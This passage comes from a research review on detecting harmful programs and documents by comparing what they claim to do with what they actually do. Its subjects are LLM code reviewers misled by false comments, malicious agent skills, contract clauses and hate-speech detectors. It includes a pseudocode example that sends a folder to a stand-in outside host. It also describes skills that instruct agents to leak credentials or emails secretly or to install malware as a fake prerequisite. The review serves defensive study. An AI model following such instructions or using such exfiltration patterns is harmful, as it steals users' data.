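For the harmful `build_wellness_report`, the third step should produce an entry such as "lines 2–3: reads every file in V1 and sends the contents to outside.example". The fourth step reveals that the author presents this as a wellness report. The model might still classify the effect as acceptable, but it can't omit the effect, which is already on the list.

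Researchers have tested parts of this procedure, but none have tested all four steps together. The results for removing comments are mixed. In Thornton's tests, removing them raised detection from 94.0% to 96.9% for Claude Opus 4.6 and from 91.9% to 95.9% for GPT-5.2, but lowered it from 93.0% to 89.0% for DeepSeek Chat and from 92.0% to 91.0% for Perplexity's Sonar Pro. Thornton concludes that removing comments hurts weaker models and advises against it. The evidence for this is thin, because DeepSeek Chat had also scored 89.0% on the versions that never had comments. Removing the comments therefore only cancelled a gain that was not statistically significant in Thornton's own test.

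The gains may also be overstated. Thornton tested the defences on several kinds of false comment, some of which appeared only in 30 relatively easy programs, while the figures without a defence come from all 100 programs.

For the second step, it matters that a program does the renaming before the model sees the code. Shen and colleagues told models that the names might be wrong and asked them to substitute placeholders themselves before summarising. This narrowed the gap between results with original and misleading names but didn't close it. The models could still see the misleading names, as Claude Opus 4.6 could when it kept them despite instructions to check.

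Instructions can make models less likely to be misled by comments. In Thornton's tests, false comments caused 14 misses with a plain prompt and four with a prompt that told the models to treat comments as untrusted. But Mitropoulos and colleagues noticed that some reviews still referred to notes the model had been told to ignore, which deleting the notes beforehand would prevent.

Even meaningless names can affect a model's verdict. When Moon and colleagues replaced variable names with random 24-letter strings, GPT-4o recognised 55.4% of incorrect Python programs, down from 63.1%. The effect grew with name length, so short placeholders such as `V1` are a better choice.

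The line numbers in the third step let a reviewer check the model's claims, but they don't make those claims accurate. Mitropoulos and colleagues required a line number and a code fragment with every flag, but 58% to 71% of the flags on vulnerable files under the neutral prompt didn't identify the real flaw.

A rigid procedure can also narrow what a model looks for. When Thornton had the models list data sources and sinks and trace the paths between them, false comments caused ten misses, compared with four under the simpler warning. Thornton suggests that the fixed method made it harder to notice unexpected problems, such as timing-dependent errors. The request for a list of effects should therefore end with an open question about anything else that looks wrong.

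The closest test of the fourth step is Thornton's two-pass review. A model reads the code once with comments and once without, and a flaw counts as found if either pass reports it. This method detected 96.1% of the flaws at twice the cost of a single pass. A second pass can add false alarms, as a longer keyword list can, but Thornton didn't measure them.

Giving the model warnings from a static analyser did slightly better, at 96.9%, and took only a single pass. But Thornton had already confirmed that static analysers could detect every flaw in the test, so the warnings were unusually likely to point to the answer. They would help less with flaws that those tools miss.

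### What the placeholders hide

Placeholders also remove useful information. A model can infer that data is sensitive from the variable name `patient_notes`, but not from `V7`. If a program calls `user_agreed` and the function's code is available, a placeholder helps, because the model has to check whether the function really asks the user. If the code is in another file, the name may be the only clue to what the function does. Random parameter names made LLMxCPG miss many more flaws in unfamiliar code, so a reviewer shouldn't treat a clean result from the blind pass as final.

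Missing code is even harder to catch, because a list of what a program does won't show a permission check that someone forgot to write. Mitropoulos and colleagues examined 34 flaws that all four of the older models they tested missed after the false claim. These flaws typically came from missing or weakened protections. A comment such as "only the owner can delete this" may be the best clue that a check should be there. Restoring the names and comments gives the model a chance to detect that the code doesn't match them.

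Very long files need another step first, such as extracting the relevant slices, because removing a few comments won't help a model that can't find the harmful part among megabytes of library code. An automatic system also needs a rule for reviews that produce no verdict. Some models in Cloudflare's tests returned garbled text or refused to answer when a file contained huge numbers of comments. In Guzmán Lorenzo's tests, Claude Opus 4.6 refused all five times when the prompt presented a harmless program as a security matter. A system that blocks only what the model labels as harmful would let these files through, so a person should review any file that gets no verdict.

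## Comparing stated purpose with actual behaviour

The last step of a name-blind review is to check whether the author's wording accounts for every effect on the list. For some programs, the whole verdict depends on that step. Here is one:

```
function copy_folder(folder):
    contents = read_all(folder)
    send(contents, "outside.example")
```

The harmful `build_wellness_report` does the same thing as a backup tool that someone might install to keep an off-site copy of her files, so data-flow analysis and a sandbox run give the same result for both. The two programs differ in what the user installed each one for, whether she agreed to the copying, and whether outside.example is her own storage or a stranger's.

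Honest and harmful programs often need the same operations. This is the *dual-use problem*. *Checking App Behavior Against App Descriptions* (Gorla, Tavecchia and colleagues, 2014) gives examples from Android phones. An app that texts a premium number may be defrauding its user, but games also used such texts as a legitimate way to charge for extra features. An app that uploads the user's contacts may be stealing them, but WhatsApp also uploaded contacts when a user first started it. The problem is just as common in software for AI agents. *SkillScreen* (Huang, Quan and colleagues, 2026) points out that harmless developer tools also run system commands, read credentials and contact remote servers.

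Users agree to have their files copied when they install a backup tool, but not when they install a step counter. The auditor therefore needs a statement of the program's purpose as evidence of what the user agreed to.

### The comparison in five steps

1. Read the description and write down the claimed purpose in a sentence. If the user asked for a particular task, write that down too.
2. List the operations that this purpose needs.
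3. List the operations the program actually contains or performs, using data-flow analysis, a sandbox run or a language model.
4. Find the excess. If N is the set of needed operations and F is the set of operations found, the excess is E = F \ N.
5. For each operation in E, ask whether it serves the purpose in some way that the second step overlooked.

It helps to finish the second step before starting the third, because a reviewer who has already seen an upload can usually think of a reason for it. Each entry should also name the data and the destination. If a reviewer writes only "sends data", the backup tool and a program that sends the same files to a thief have identical lists.

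| Program and claimed purpose | Needed | Found | Excess |
|---|---|---|---|
| `copy_folder`: backs up a folder to the user's storage | read the folder, send it to the user's storage | read the folder, send it to outside.example | none, if the user's storage is at outside.example |
| `build_wellness_report` (harmful): reports step counts | read the step-count log, print the count | read every file, send them all to outside.example | reading the other files, sending anything |
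| `build_wellness_report` (honest): reports step counts | read the step-count log, print the count | read the step-count log, print the count | none |

In the second row, neither reading a bank statement nor sending it helps report step counts, so both operations remain unexplained after the fifth step. The harmful program also never prints a step count. A missing operation like this is another clue, although an author could easily add it.

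The fifth step matters more in milder cases. Suppose the honest program also contacts its developer's server once a week to check for a newer version, and sends only its own version number. The program doesn't need to do this to count the user's steps, so the check belongs in the excess, but it helps the user and reveals very little. A reviewer might accept it and ask the author to mention it in the description.

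### Learning what an app needs from similar apps

The second step is hard to automate because nobody publishes a list of the operations that a restaurant guide app needs. CHABADA, a system by Gorla and colleagues, learned such lists from other apps, without any sentences labelled by hand. An earlier system, WHYPER, relied on such labels to check whether an app's description gave a reason for requesting a permission.

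The researchers downloaded popular free apps from Google Play and kept 22,521 that had a usable English description and contained at least one sensitive function. They counted a function as sensitive if Android requires the user's permission for it, such as reading the phone's location. They used a statistical method to identify 30 topics in the descriptions, then a second method to sort the apps by these topics into 32 groups, such as "navigation and travel". Within each group, CHABADA learned which sensitive functions were normal and ranked the apps by how far they departed from that pattern.

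An app called London Restaurants was in the travel group. Apps in that group normally used the internet and the phone's location, but this one also retrieved the phone's number, device identifier and list of user accounts. It sent this information to an advertising service that the app's description didn't mention.

One of the researchers examined the five most unusual apps in each group, 160 in all, and classified 42 as malicious, 20 as dubious and 98 as harmless. The team then tested CHABADA on 172 known malicious apps, none of which it had seen in training:

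| What CHABADA compared each app with | Malicious apps missed | Harmless apps flagged |
|---|---|---|
| All other apps together | 76% | 15% |
| Apps in the same Google Play category | 53% | 16% |
| Apps with similar descriptions | 44% | 16% |

The false-alarm rate hardly changed, so the fall in misses is good evidence that it helps to compare an app with others that have the same purpose. But only about a fifth of the flags in this test were correct, and the share would be lower in a store where malicious apps are rarer. *Mining Android Apps for Anomalies* (Kuznetsov, Gorla and colleagues, 2014) describes a revised version that missed 26% of malicious apps and flagged about 11% of harmless ones. Among other changes, it gave less weight to functions common within a group.

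The malicious apps in the test had no descriptions of their own. Many were altered copies of genuine apps, so the researchers used the originals' descriptions. This is a fair test for malware that poses as a known app, but not for malware with a description written to fit it.

CHABADA learned what apps in each group commonly did, which isn't always what their purpose requires. Many apps in the "money" group contained advertising code that collected personal information, so CHABADA flagged two poker games in that group for not collecting any.

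### When an agent carries out the description

A false app description can mislead a buyer, but it can't steal anything by itself because the phone doesn't execute it. An agent does act on the text in a skill, so that text can lead directly to theft. *SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, 2026) explains that a skill file typically opens with a name and a description, which tell the agent when to load it, followed by a body of instructions that the agent treats as authoritative. In one example, the description offers help with a programming library, but the body includes a "health check" that sends the user's private login key to an outsider.

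If the wellness program were a skill, it might contain no code, because a sentence telling the agent to send the folder to outside.example would have the same effect as `send`. The reviewer therefore has to treat the opening description as a claim, covered in the first step, and the instructions as behaviour, covered in the third step along with any scripts.

Some instructions are hard to reconcile with any honest purpose. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes an email skill that instructed the agent to copy every message to an outside address, not to ask permission, and not to mention it in conversation. An email tool might have a reason to copy messages to a company archive, for example, but it has no obvious reason to hide this from the user.

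The third step also requires examining the operations themselves. Huang and colleagues tested detectors on pairs of skills that differed only in their commands. In one pair, the harmless command reports free disk space and the harmful one deletes files. Their small model, trained to score skill text, flagged all 90 harmless skills along with all 90 harmful ones. GPT-5.5, a larger general-purpose model from OpenAI, flagged none of the harmless ones.

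### What the documentation leaves out

Liu and colleagues made one of the largest comparisons of documentation and behaviour so far. In January 2026, they collected 98,380 skills from two public registries and searched them for 14 suspicious patterns, such as reading credentials or downloading code and running it. They used regular expressions for the scripts and added a language model for the instructions. The search left 4,287 candidates.

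They then ran every candidate in a sandbox with decoy credentials, and 762 showed at least one sign of harm. Two researchers compared each one's behaviour with its documentation and confirmed 157 as malicious. Most of the other 605 were harmless tools for security-related work, including credential managers and *penetration-testing* tools, which attack a system to find its weak points. Only about one in five of the candidates that showed signs of harm were therefore confirmed as malicious, and people had to consider purpose to distinguish them from the others.

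Of the 157 malicious skills, 115 (73%) had at least one function that readers couldn't infer from the documentation. The most common was contacting an undocumented internet address. Liu and colleagues conclude that comparing documentation with behaviour is the most productive way to detect malicious skills.

That may be right, but the 73% doesn't establish it. Hidden functionality is one of the behaviours in their definition of a malicious skill, and they don't report how many harmless skills also have undocumented functions. They argue that honest developers have no reason to hide anything, but developers can leave things out without meaning to hide them. Gorla and colleagues found that Yahoo! Mail could send text messages and that the training app Runtastic could record audio, and neither app's description explained why.

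Liu and colleagues also report that undocumented functions are more common in more sophisticated attacks, rising from 0% of basic skills to 100% of advanced ones. Those two figures follow from the definitions, which class a skill as basic only if it has no undocumented functions and as advanced only if it has at least one.

In one case, someone copied a legitimate skill for making presentations and added three lines to a file of 484. The new lines told the agent to run a "backup" script, which silently uploaded the user's files to an outside server. A reviewer might mistake this for an ordinary backup tool unless they had first listed what a presentation tool needs, which would not include an outside server.

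The figure of 157 is a lower bound. The researchers never ran the 94,093 skills that matched no pattern. When they rechecked a tenth of the unconfirmed candidates by hand, about 2% were attacks the sandbox had missed, which suggests around 80 more among all the candidates. Another 93% of that sample contained triggers that hadn't fired within the 60-second limit, and it is unclear how many would have done harm.

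The registries removed all 157 skills after Liu and colleagues reported them, which supports the labels but makes the work harder to repeat. Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *MALSKILLS*, could retrieve only 57 of them. They ran the published detection software on those 57, and it detected six. The software evidently can't reproduce the result on its own, but the original labels may still be right, since a skill's repository can change and the servers it contacts can disappear.

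### A prerequisite the task doesn't need

Malicious skills can also place the harm in a step before the task. *MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, 2026) collected 703 malicious skills that attackers had published, and 86.3% of them declared a fake prerequisite. The task looked harmless, but the skill told the agent to install another program first. This program was malware, usually with a name that sounded trustworthy.

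Two researchers confirmed these 703 skills by reading them. The sample is narrow because 81% came from two accounts, and a single campaign to steal cryptocurrency dominated it. The 86.3% therefore mostly reflects what a few attackers did many times, and the next campaign could look quite different.

A reviewer who compares purpose and behaviour carelessly can miss a fake prerequisite. Many legitimate skills depend on other software, so installing a program can look like part of the task. The reviewer has to check whether this task needs this particular program, and whether the file comes from the program's real publisher. One skill in the collection was presented as a helper for Google's office software. Such a skill plausibly needs access to the user's Google account, but not an unfamiliar program from an unrelated address.

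Because the published attacks were so alike, Guo, Jia and colleagues also generated new ones to cover a wider range. They checked the labels on the new attacks by having an agent run each skill in a sandbox, and kept 3,214 of 3,757 candidates. Candidates passed 94.5% of the time when the harm was in code and 75.8% of the time when it was only in the instructions.

The check is weaker for harmful instructions because a skill passed whether the agent obeyed the instruction or recognised and refused it. Its label therefore shows that the skill contains a recognisable attack, but the attack may never have succeeded. Two reviewers examined 300 of the generated skills and agreed with every label.

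A third group of generated skills split the harm between instructions and code. For example, the instructions told the agent to prepare a file, and a script then used that file to do the damage. Neither part had to look fully malicious by itself. Guo, Jia and colleagues conclude that a reviewer has to consider the task, the instructions and the code together.

### Connecting evidence across files

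Wang and colleagues built a system called MalSkills for this kind of case. Their main example is a skill that claims to help with remote-access problems. Its instructions tell the agent to collect diagnostic information. A settings file adds the user's cloud credentials and supplies an upload address, and a script sends everything there. Each file looks plausible for a troubleshooting tool, and a reviewer can see the excess only by connecting them. A support team might need error logs but shouldn't need a customer's cloud credentials.

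MalSkills first extracts sensitive operations from all of a skill's files, using 2,665 pattern rules and a language model. It then builds a graph that connects operations when data passes from one to another, even across files. Finally, it searches the graph for known harmful patterns and uses a language model to assess the connected operations in context.

The researchers tested the system on 100 malicious and 100 popular harmless skills, then removed one component at a time. (Their test set is called MalSkillsBench, which is easily confused with MalSkillBench.)

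| Version of MalSkills | Miss rate | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|
| Complete | 8% | 5% |
| Without the rules that extract operations | 73% | 0% |
| Without the language model that extracts operations | 9% | 5% |
| Without the fixed patterns that judge the graph | 8% | 5% |
| Without the language model that judges the graph | 18% | 49% |

Finding operations depended almost entirely on the rules, and judging them depended almost entirely on the language model. Without the model's judgment, the fixed patterns flagged almost half of the harmless skills. This is the dual-use problem again, since even connected chains of sensitive operations are common in honest skills, and something has to assess what they are for. However, Wang and colleagues didn't have the model write down the needed operations first, so their results don't directly test the five-step method.

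In a larger test, MalSkills flagged 620 of 150,108 skills from seven registries, and manual review confirmed 400 of them. At most 220 flags were false alarms, about 0.15% of all the skills, far below the 5% in the smaller test. The rate may have been higher in the smaller test because popular skills do more that looks suspicious. The skills wrongly flagged there tended to contain installation steps, scheduled tasks or instructions for collecting data from websites.

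Most of the attacks that MalSkills missed in the test were written in prose, with no explicit sensitive operation to extract. Some directed people to download software from elsewhere. This is worrying because the fake prerequisites that dominate MalSkillBench's published attacks work in a similar way.

### Descriptions that permit too much

A broader description can make the comparison useless. Broadening the claimed purpose can add operations to N but cannot remove any, so E can only shrink or stay the same. If the harmful wellness program were described as "a personal assistant that organises your files and keeps them in sync online", reading the folder and sending it away would both seem necessary.

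Before accepting a sensitive operation, a reviewer can require the description to make clear which data the program uses and where it sends them. "Keeps your files in sync" doesn't say where the files go, so the reviewer would treat the upload as unexplained until the developer names the destination. This rule also burdens honest developers who write short descriptions. The CHABADA study excluded apps with fewer than ten useful words of description, but a registry can't ignore its worst-documented software. It could return the submission and ask for a specific statement.

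Automatic systems can also misinterpret an honest description. CHABADA grouped a keyboard app with language-learning apps because more than half of the app's description was about the languages it supported. It then compared the keyboard's behaviour with what language-learning apps normally do.

### Purposes that are harmful in themselves

If an app's description says it forwards a partner's private messages without the partner's knowledge, and the app does exactly that, comparing its stated purpose with its behaviour reveals no discrepancy. The comparison protects the person who installs a program from being deceived about it, but in this case the victim is the partner. A reviewer therefore has to assess the stated purpose before using it to justify the program's behaviour, by asking whom the program affects and whether those people have agreed.

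Disclosure can also make a doubtful practice look normal. Gorla and colleagues note that if London Restaurants had disclosed its data collection, CHABADA would have grouped it with advertising apps, where it would no longer have stood out. In the study by Liu and colleagues, 42 of the 157 malicious skills had no undocumented functions, so a check that looked only for such functions would have missed them.

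Penetration-testing tools perform the same operations as an attacker's tools and are openly described that way, but their purpose is legitimate if the owner of the target system has agreed. That agreement is usually in a contract or an email, which the reviewer won't find in the software.

### Assurances that nobody has checked

An author who knows that reviewers compare claims with behaviour can make false claims. One publisher released 85 of the 157 skills that Liu and colleagues confirmed, each impersonating a different brand. All 85 contained the same assurances, including "Your credentials, your choice" and a promise that the skill never transmits credentials, but they also installed code from an outside server.

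Tests by Mitropoulos and colleagues showed that a language model can easily mistake such a promise for evidence. The reviewer should therefore use the description only to decide what belongs in N. F has to come from the code, the instructions or a sandbox run, and nothing the author writes should remove an operation from it.

A specific assurance can still help, because the reviewer can test it. If the author promises that a skill never transmits credentials and a decoy credential turns up in its outgoing traffic, the upload contradicts the promise. This is stronger evidence of dishonesty than an upload the author never mentioned, which an honest author might have forgotten to disclose.

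## Auditing documents by what they do

Apart from skill files and other text that an agent carries out, documents mostly have effects because people read them and act on them, or because someone can enforce them. A reviewer can't trace data through a contract or run a chat message in a sandbox, so they ask what each sentence does. A sentence can request, promise, threaten or permit an action, oblige someone to take it, or instruct someone how to do it.

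Philosophers use the term *speech acts* for actions performed with words, such as promising. *Privacy Washing* (Brackin, 2026) applies John Searle's account of them to privacy policies. A company that writes "we do not sell your personal information" is making a promise, which creates an obligation.

The same act can have many wordings. "Send me the code", "I need the code before I can help you" and "your refund is waiting for the code" all request a code. A sentence can also perform different acts depending on who says it. "I know where you live" may be a threat from a stranger, but from a friend it may just mean that you don't need to send directions.

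### Reading a document act by act

An audit of this kind can follow five steps:

1. Write the rule first, as a statement that is either true or false of the document.
2. Break the document into single acts. A sentence with "and" or "unless" in it often contains more than one.
3. For each act, write down the actor, the action, the affected party, the condition and the consequence. Leave a blank where the document doesn't supply one.
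4. Replace headings, labels and defined terms with what they mean in this document.
5. Ask whether the acts, taken together, entail the statement in the rule.

A text *entails* a statement if the statement is true in every situation in which the text holds. "Every member pays £20 a month" entails "a member who joined yesterday pays £20 a month", but not "members pay by card". In the fifth step, the result is a breach if the document entails the statement and a pass if it entails the opposite. If it entails neither, the reviewer is missing a fact and should look for it before giving a verdict.

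The fourth step is like replacing names with placeholders in code, and it has a similar exception. Some words in a contract have legal effect, as the UK Supreme Court's judgment on penalty clauses shows, so the reviewer should keep the original wording beside the plain version.

### The subscription clause again

The twelve-month subscription from the first section costs £20 a month. Suppose the rule forbids contracts of which this is true: "A member who leaves early has to pay for months in which the seller provides nothing." (This rule is invented for the example and doesn't state any country's law.) The two harmful clauses produce these records:

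| | Blunt wording | Friendly wording |
|---|---|---|
| Clause | "Exit penalty: a member who cancels must pay every remaining monthly charge." | "Loyalty completion: on leaving, a member settles the balance of the plan year." |
| Act | obliges | obliges |
| Actor | the member | the member |
| Action | pays every remaining monthly charge | pays the balance of the plan year |
| Affected party | the member, who loses the money | the member, who loses the money |
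| Condition | the member cancels | the member leaves |
| Consequence after three months | the member owes £180 | the member owes £180, if "balance" means the remaining charges |

Without the headings, most of the difference in tone is gone. The friendly clause doesn't contain "must", but in a contract "a member settles" still creates an obligation. A reviewer who looked for obligations by searching for "must" and "shall" would miss it.

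Neither clause breaks the rule by itself, because neither specifies whether the member keeps access to the service. But if another clause reads "Access ends on the day a member leaves," that clause and the blunt clause together entail the forbidden statement, because the member pays for nine months and receives nothing. If members kept access until the end of the year, the same £180 would not break this rule.

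The friendly clause also doesn't say whether "balance" means the remaining charges or what the member already owes for the months she has used. If the contract defines it as the charges for the rest of the term, both clauses have the same effect. If the contract doesn't define it, the reviewer should record the result as undetermined and ask the seller how much a member who leaves after three months would pay, because a specific amount is harder to soften with friendly wording.

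The harmless clause from the same grid, "No penalty, forfeiture or termination fee applies to a member who cancels", is a promise by the seller. If the same contract also contains the loyalty clause, that clause seems to break the promise.

### Automatic audits of contracts

Researchers still do some of this work by hand. *Terms of (Ab)Use* (2026), for example, annotates the terms of six generative AI services, with a focus on the EU. Most online contracts will never get that much attention, so other researchers have tried to automate the work.

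*Text to Trust* (Juttu, Singireddy and colleagues, 2025) used 9,414 clauses from online contracts, of which people had labelled 1,032 unfair. In one fair clause, the company asks customers to check the latest rates before they make a call. One unfair clause lets the company change its call rates at any time without notice, by posting the change on its website. Both clauses are about call rates, but only the second gives the company a power over the customer.

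The researchers gave five OpenAI models a list of types of unfair terms, such as those that limit the provider's liability or let it change the contract on its own. The models found 89% to 92% of the unfair clauses, but only 29% to 43% of their flags were correct. BERT, a much smaller and older model that the researchers had trained on labelled clauses, found 89% of the unfair clauses, and 89% of its flags were correct.

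This makes the trained model look twice as precise, but the comparison is misleading. The paper describes one test set for both, yet the reported accuracies fit only if about half of the clauses in BERT's test were unfair and about 11% in the other models' test. The false-alarm rates that follow from the published figures are much closer together:

| Model | Miss rate | False-alarm rate | Reported precision | Precision if 11% of clauses are unfair |
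|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, prompted | 11% | 26% | 29% | 29% |
| o3-mini, prompted | 9% | 15% | 43% | 43% |
| BERT, trained | 11% | about 11% | 89% | about 50% |

On an ordinary contract, about half of BERT's flags would also be wrong. All these models are well behind current ones, which may do better.

A more basic problem is that the models labelled clauses with little or none of the surrounding contract. Given the friendly subscription clause, a model would not have seen the definition of "balance" or the clause about access, so it could only have guessed. Juttu and colleagues also ran BERT on 937 entries from real websites, and it flagged 188. Nobody had labelled those entries, so the number of correct flags is unknown.

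### Promises that the same document breaks

Brackin searches whole privacy policies for commitments, such as a promise not to share data, that conflict with a practice the company describes elsewhere in the same policy. Its method resembles the act-by-act procedure. Three language models split each policy into statements of about 10 to 30 words and label each one as a commitment or a practice. They also record who acts, what happens to the data, under what conditions, and with what qualifications. The study keeps only statements that at least two of the models extracted.

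The system then pairs every commitment with every practice in the same policy. For 123 companies' policies, collected in January 2026, this gave 95,585 pairs. Filters removed most of them, such as those where the two statements concerned different actors or the commitment already contained an exception for the practice. A *natural language inference* model, which is trained to detect whether one sentence entails or contradicts another, then scored the rest. A panel of three language models reviewed 293 of the flagged pairs and confirmed 32 contradictions, in the policies of 15 of the 123 companies (12%). The run took about two hours and cost about $8.

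One confirmed pair shows how entailment can reveal an apparent conflict between statements that share few words. A large retailer promises not to give third parties its customers' text-messaging consent data for their own marketing. Elsewhere it describes disclosing "all categories of personal information" to certain kinds of third party. "All categories" includes the consent data, so the second statement seems to permit what the first rules out.

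Other cases depend on a word's legal meaning. A company might promise not to sell personal information but also say it passes customer identifiers to advertising partners. That may not be a sale in everyday English, but California's attorney general determined in the 2022 Sephora case that sharing data with advertising partners was a sale under the state's privacy law. A reviewer who doesn't know the legal definition can't complete the fifth step.

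The 12% figure could be too high or too low. No privacy lawyers checked the panel's verdicts. Brackin reviewed all the confirmed cases and found none clearly wrong, but knew the panel's answers beforehand. Some of the cases compare a promise about one product with a general statement about the company, which the panel was instructed not to count. The figure could be too low because the system sent the panel only pairs with fairly similar wording. A later run with different models gave 13% with that restriction and 20% without it, so the wording filter was excluding a good part of what the study was looking for.

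The study also gives a reason not to leave the entailment question to a specialised model. Such models exceed 90% accuracy on general tests, but Brackin cites one that reached only 66% on questions about statutes. In the policy audit, the panel rejected about nine in ten of the flagged pairs it judged.

General language models find different contradictions depending on the model and prompt. *A Systematic Evaluation of Traditional Privacy Policy Analysis Tools Against LLMs* (2026) describes a test on ten privacy policies. Two older tools, which look for direct logical contradictions such as "we collect" and "we do not collect", found no true ones. Each combination of language model and prompt reported about 31 on average, but none of the contradictions that the researchers confirmed was found by every combination. A single run can therefore miss a real contradiction even if it reports many.

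### Tests with the same word in different uses

The most developed tests of functional auditing for text concern short messages. HateCheck, which Röttger and colleagues published in 2021, is a *functional test suite*, a set of short cases grouped by the ability each one tests. One group contains non-hateful profanity, and another contains people quoting hateful remarks to object to them. Developers can use the results to identify which abilities a hate speech detector lacks, which they could not do with a single accuracy figure.

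Many of the cases share a word with another case that uses it for a different purpose. Sabadin and colleagues reprint several, including the harmless "We fought hard for queer rights" and a case that uses "queer" to belittle the person addressed. Röttger and colleagues ran the suite on four detectors, including two commercial services. The detectors correctly classified only about 18% to 40% of the harmless uses of reclaimed slurs, but almost all of the harmless profanity. Sabadin and colleagues suggest that the training data contained plenty of friendly swearing but few slurs used in solidarity. If so, the good result on profanity may not show that the detectors can identify what a word is being used for.

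XSTest, published in 2024 by a group that also included Röttger, applies the idea to chatbots that refuse too much. It contrasts 250 safe prompts with 200 unsafe ones (Tuzhykov, *SITO*, 2026). A safe prompt might ask how to kill a frozen computer program, and its unsafe contrast might ask how to kill a neighbour. A chatbot that refuses both is probably reacting to the word "kill", while one that answers both hasn't recognised the threat.

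### Five systems in eleven languages

Sabadin and colleagues tested five systems: an English keyword filter, a toxicity classifier, and three *guard models*, which are language models trained to label text as safe or unsafe. Two of the guard models are a small and a larger version of Qwen3Guard, from the Chinese company Alibaba. The third, PolyGuard, is a research model trained for 17 languages.

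The researchers used HateCheck and its later versions in ten other languages. The harmless sentences resembled hate speech, for example because they quoted it or contained a negated insult. The hateful ones were *implicit*, with no slurs, profanity or open insults. The English results were:

| System | Harmless look-alikes flagged | Implicit hate missed | Ranking score (0.5 is chance) |
|---|---|---|---|
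| Keyword filter | 52.7% | 60.7% | 0.43 |
| Toxicity classifier | 51.8% | 42.1% | 0.52 |
| Qwen3Guard, small | 41.3% | 15.0% | 0.73 |
| Qwen3Guard, larger | 26.2% | 8.6% | 0.84 |
| PolyGuard | 60.7% | 0.7% | 0.87 |
| Individual annotators | – | – | 0.99 |

The ranking score is the AUC, or balanced accuracy for the filter and the annotators, because they gave only yes-or-no verdicts. PolyGuard has the best score of the five systems. It also has the most false alarms, because its usual threshold is low for this material. A higher threshold would reduce the false alarms and increase the misses, but no threshold would bring PolyGuard up to the annotators' 0.99.

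The keyword filter caught some implicit hate, largely because the sentences contained words such as "gay" and "black", but the same words also caused its false alarms. The filter was responding to mentions of a group, which reveal little about what a sentence says about that group.

Across the languages, 51 of the 55 combinations of system and language did reliably worse than individual native speakers. Three of the four exceptions are guard models in French, where the human standard was low because the annotators labelled 55% of the supposedly harmless sentences hateful. The fourth is PolyGuard in Dutch, which scored 0.85 against the annotators' 0.90, a gap just small enough to be due to chance.

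Larger models helped, but unevenly. In nine languages, the average score rose from 0.65 for the small Qwen3Guard to 0.81 for both the larger one and PolyGuard. In Arabic and in Hindi written with Latin letters, none of the three exceeded 0.59, and the larger Qwen3Guard missed 63% of the implicit hate in Arabic and 77% in Hindi. The keyword filter's Hindi entries were in a different script, so it couldn't match anything. It missed all the hate but also flagged no harmless sentences, so it would look excellent if judged only on false alarms.

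The low scores are good evidence that these systems have trouble telling hate from harmless sentences that resemble it, but weaker evidence of why. The hateful and harmless sentences come from two separate sets and are not matched pairs, so they differ in more than function. The guard models were also designed for a different task, judging requests to a chatbot under a broad safety policy. However, HateCheck has been public since 2021, and the models may have seen parts of it in training, which could have raised their scores.

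Two of the three authors run Tuteliq, a company that sells detection based on behaviour, and the third advises it. They disclose this and tested none of its products, but they have a commercial interest in the conclusion that existing systems rely on wording. They acknowledge that the study doesn't show that a system designed to recognise behaviour would do better. Testing that would require test sets for scams, coercion and the grooming of children, which they say don't yet exist.

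*Epistemic Injustice in Language Models* (Stranisci, Pranav and colleagues, 2026), a separate study of ordinary web text, gives some support to the idea that guard models partly follow vocabulary. The verdicts of three guard models agreed with a list of sexual words at a kappa of 0.25 to 0.50, where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect agreement. This doesn't prove that the models reacted to the words, since they are also meant to flag sexual content. But two students who read 500 of the sentences would have kept 91.3% of those that a guard model had flagged. That figure isn't an everyday false-alarm rate, because the sample deliberately included many sentences on which the systems disagreed, and the students disagreed with each other on 15% of them.

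### Removing only the harmful part

A stricter test removes only what makes a message harmful. This edit is easy to get wrong because it has to remove every harmful element while keeping the topic, the sender and most of the words.

For example, a message in which a caller claiming to be from the bank asks for a security code might become one in which the bank warns the customer never to share the code.

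Tuzhykov used such *minimal-edit contrasts* to test Tuteliq Detect, a commercial service from the company mentioned above. The test set has 2,332 messages, all written by language models, about scams, money laundering, gambling harm and bullying. They are in English, Ukrainian and mixtures of Ukrainian with other languages. The contrasts were difficult to produce. In the first attempt, a checking model judged 38 of the 71 contrasts written by Google's Gemini still harmful, and Tuzhykov had them rewritten.

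The service flagged 10 of the 171 contrasts (5.8%) and 1.3% of other harmless messages on the same topics. In 139 of 149 pairs (93.3%), it classified both the harmful message and its edited version correctly, which a filter that relied on their shared words could not have done. In English, it missed 11.4% of harmful messages and flagged 1.3% of harmless ones overall.

These results are much better than those of the five open systems, but the two studies can't be compared directly because the harms, messages and systems all differ. The service also did worse on unfamiliar writing. It missed 6.4% of the harmful messages written by Anthropic's Claude and 10.5% of those by Gemini, but 9 of 28 (32%) from Alibaba's Qwen, which supplied only a small control group. The set has no messages written by people, which might be harder still. Tuteliq engaged the company that commissioned the study, supplied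 free access, and saw the manuscript only to correct factual errors.

If 1 message in 100 were harmful, only 18% to 36% of flags would be correct in the three categories where the service raised false alarms. The share of correct flags may be higher in practice, because ordinary traffic should contain fewer deceptive look-alikes than this test.

### Several questions in place of one label

Most of these detectors return a single label, which gives a reviewer little to check. *xList-Hate* (Girón, Miralles and colleagues, 2026) divides the judgment into ten yes-or-no questions. The first is whether the text targets people for a protected characteristic, such as religion or ethnicity. Others are whether it contains a slur, dehumanises the group, calls for its exclusion or encourages violence. The ninth is whether the writer endorses the message or is quoting, reporting or mocking it, a distinction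 needed to recognise counter-speech.

A language model answers each question separately, without seeing its other answers and without being asked whether the text is hate speech. The answers form a row of ten ones and zeros, with 1,024 possible combinations. A *decision tree*, a short chain of if-then choices learned from labelled examples, turns the row into a verdict. A moderator can follow the chain and see, for instance, that the verdict depended on the answer about endorsement, and someone who disagrees with the verdict can challenge that answer.

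The researchers compared the checklist with a single direct question, using eight models and five collections of text. The checklist ranked hateful texts above harmless ones more accurately in 37 of the 40 comparisons. On HateCheck, it raised the AUC of a 24-billion-parameter Mistral model from 0.877 to 0.956. But part of the gain may have come from the explanation and worked examples included with each checklist question, and from the labelled data used to train the tree, none of which the direct question had.

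Girón and colleagues also compared the checklist with models trained directly on hate-speech labels. They conclude that the checklist holds up better on unfamiliar collections, but this depends on the measure. They divide a method's score on new data by its score on the data it was trained for, so a method can look robust because it was poor to begin with. The highest average ratio in the study, 194%, came from a trained model that ranked texts far worse than chance on its own data. The checklist won only 8 of 24 comparisons by plain AUC on unfamiliar collections.

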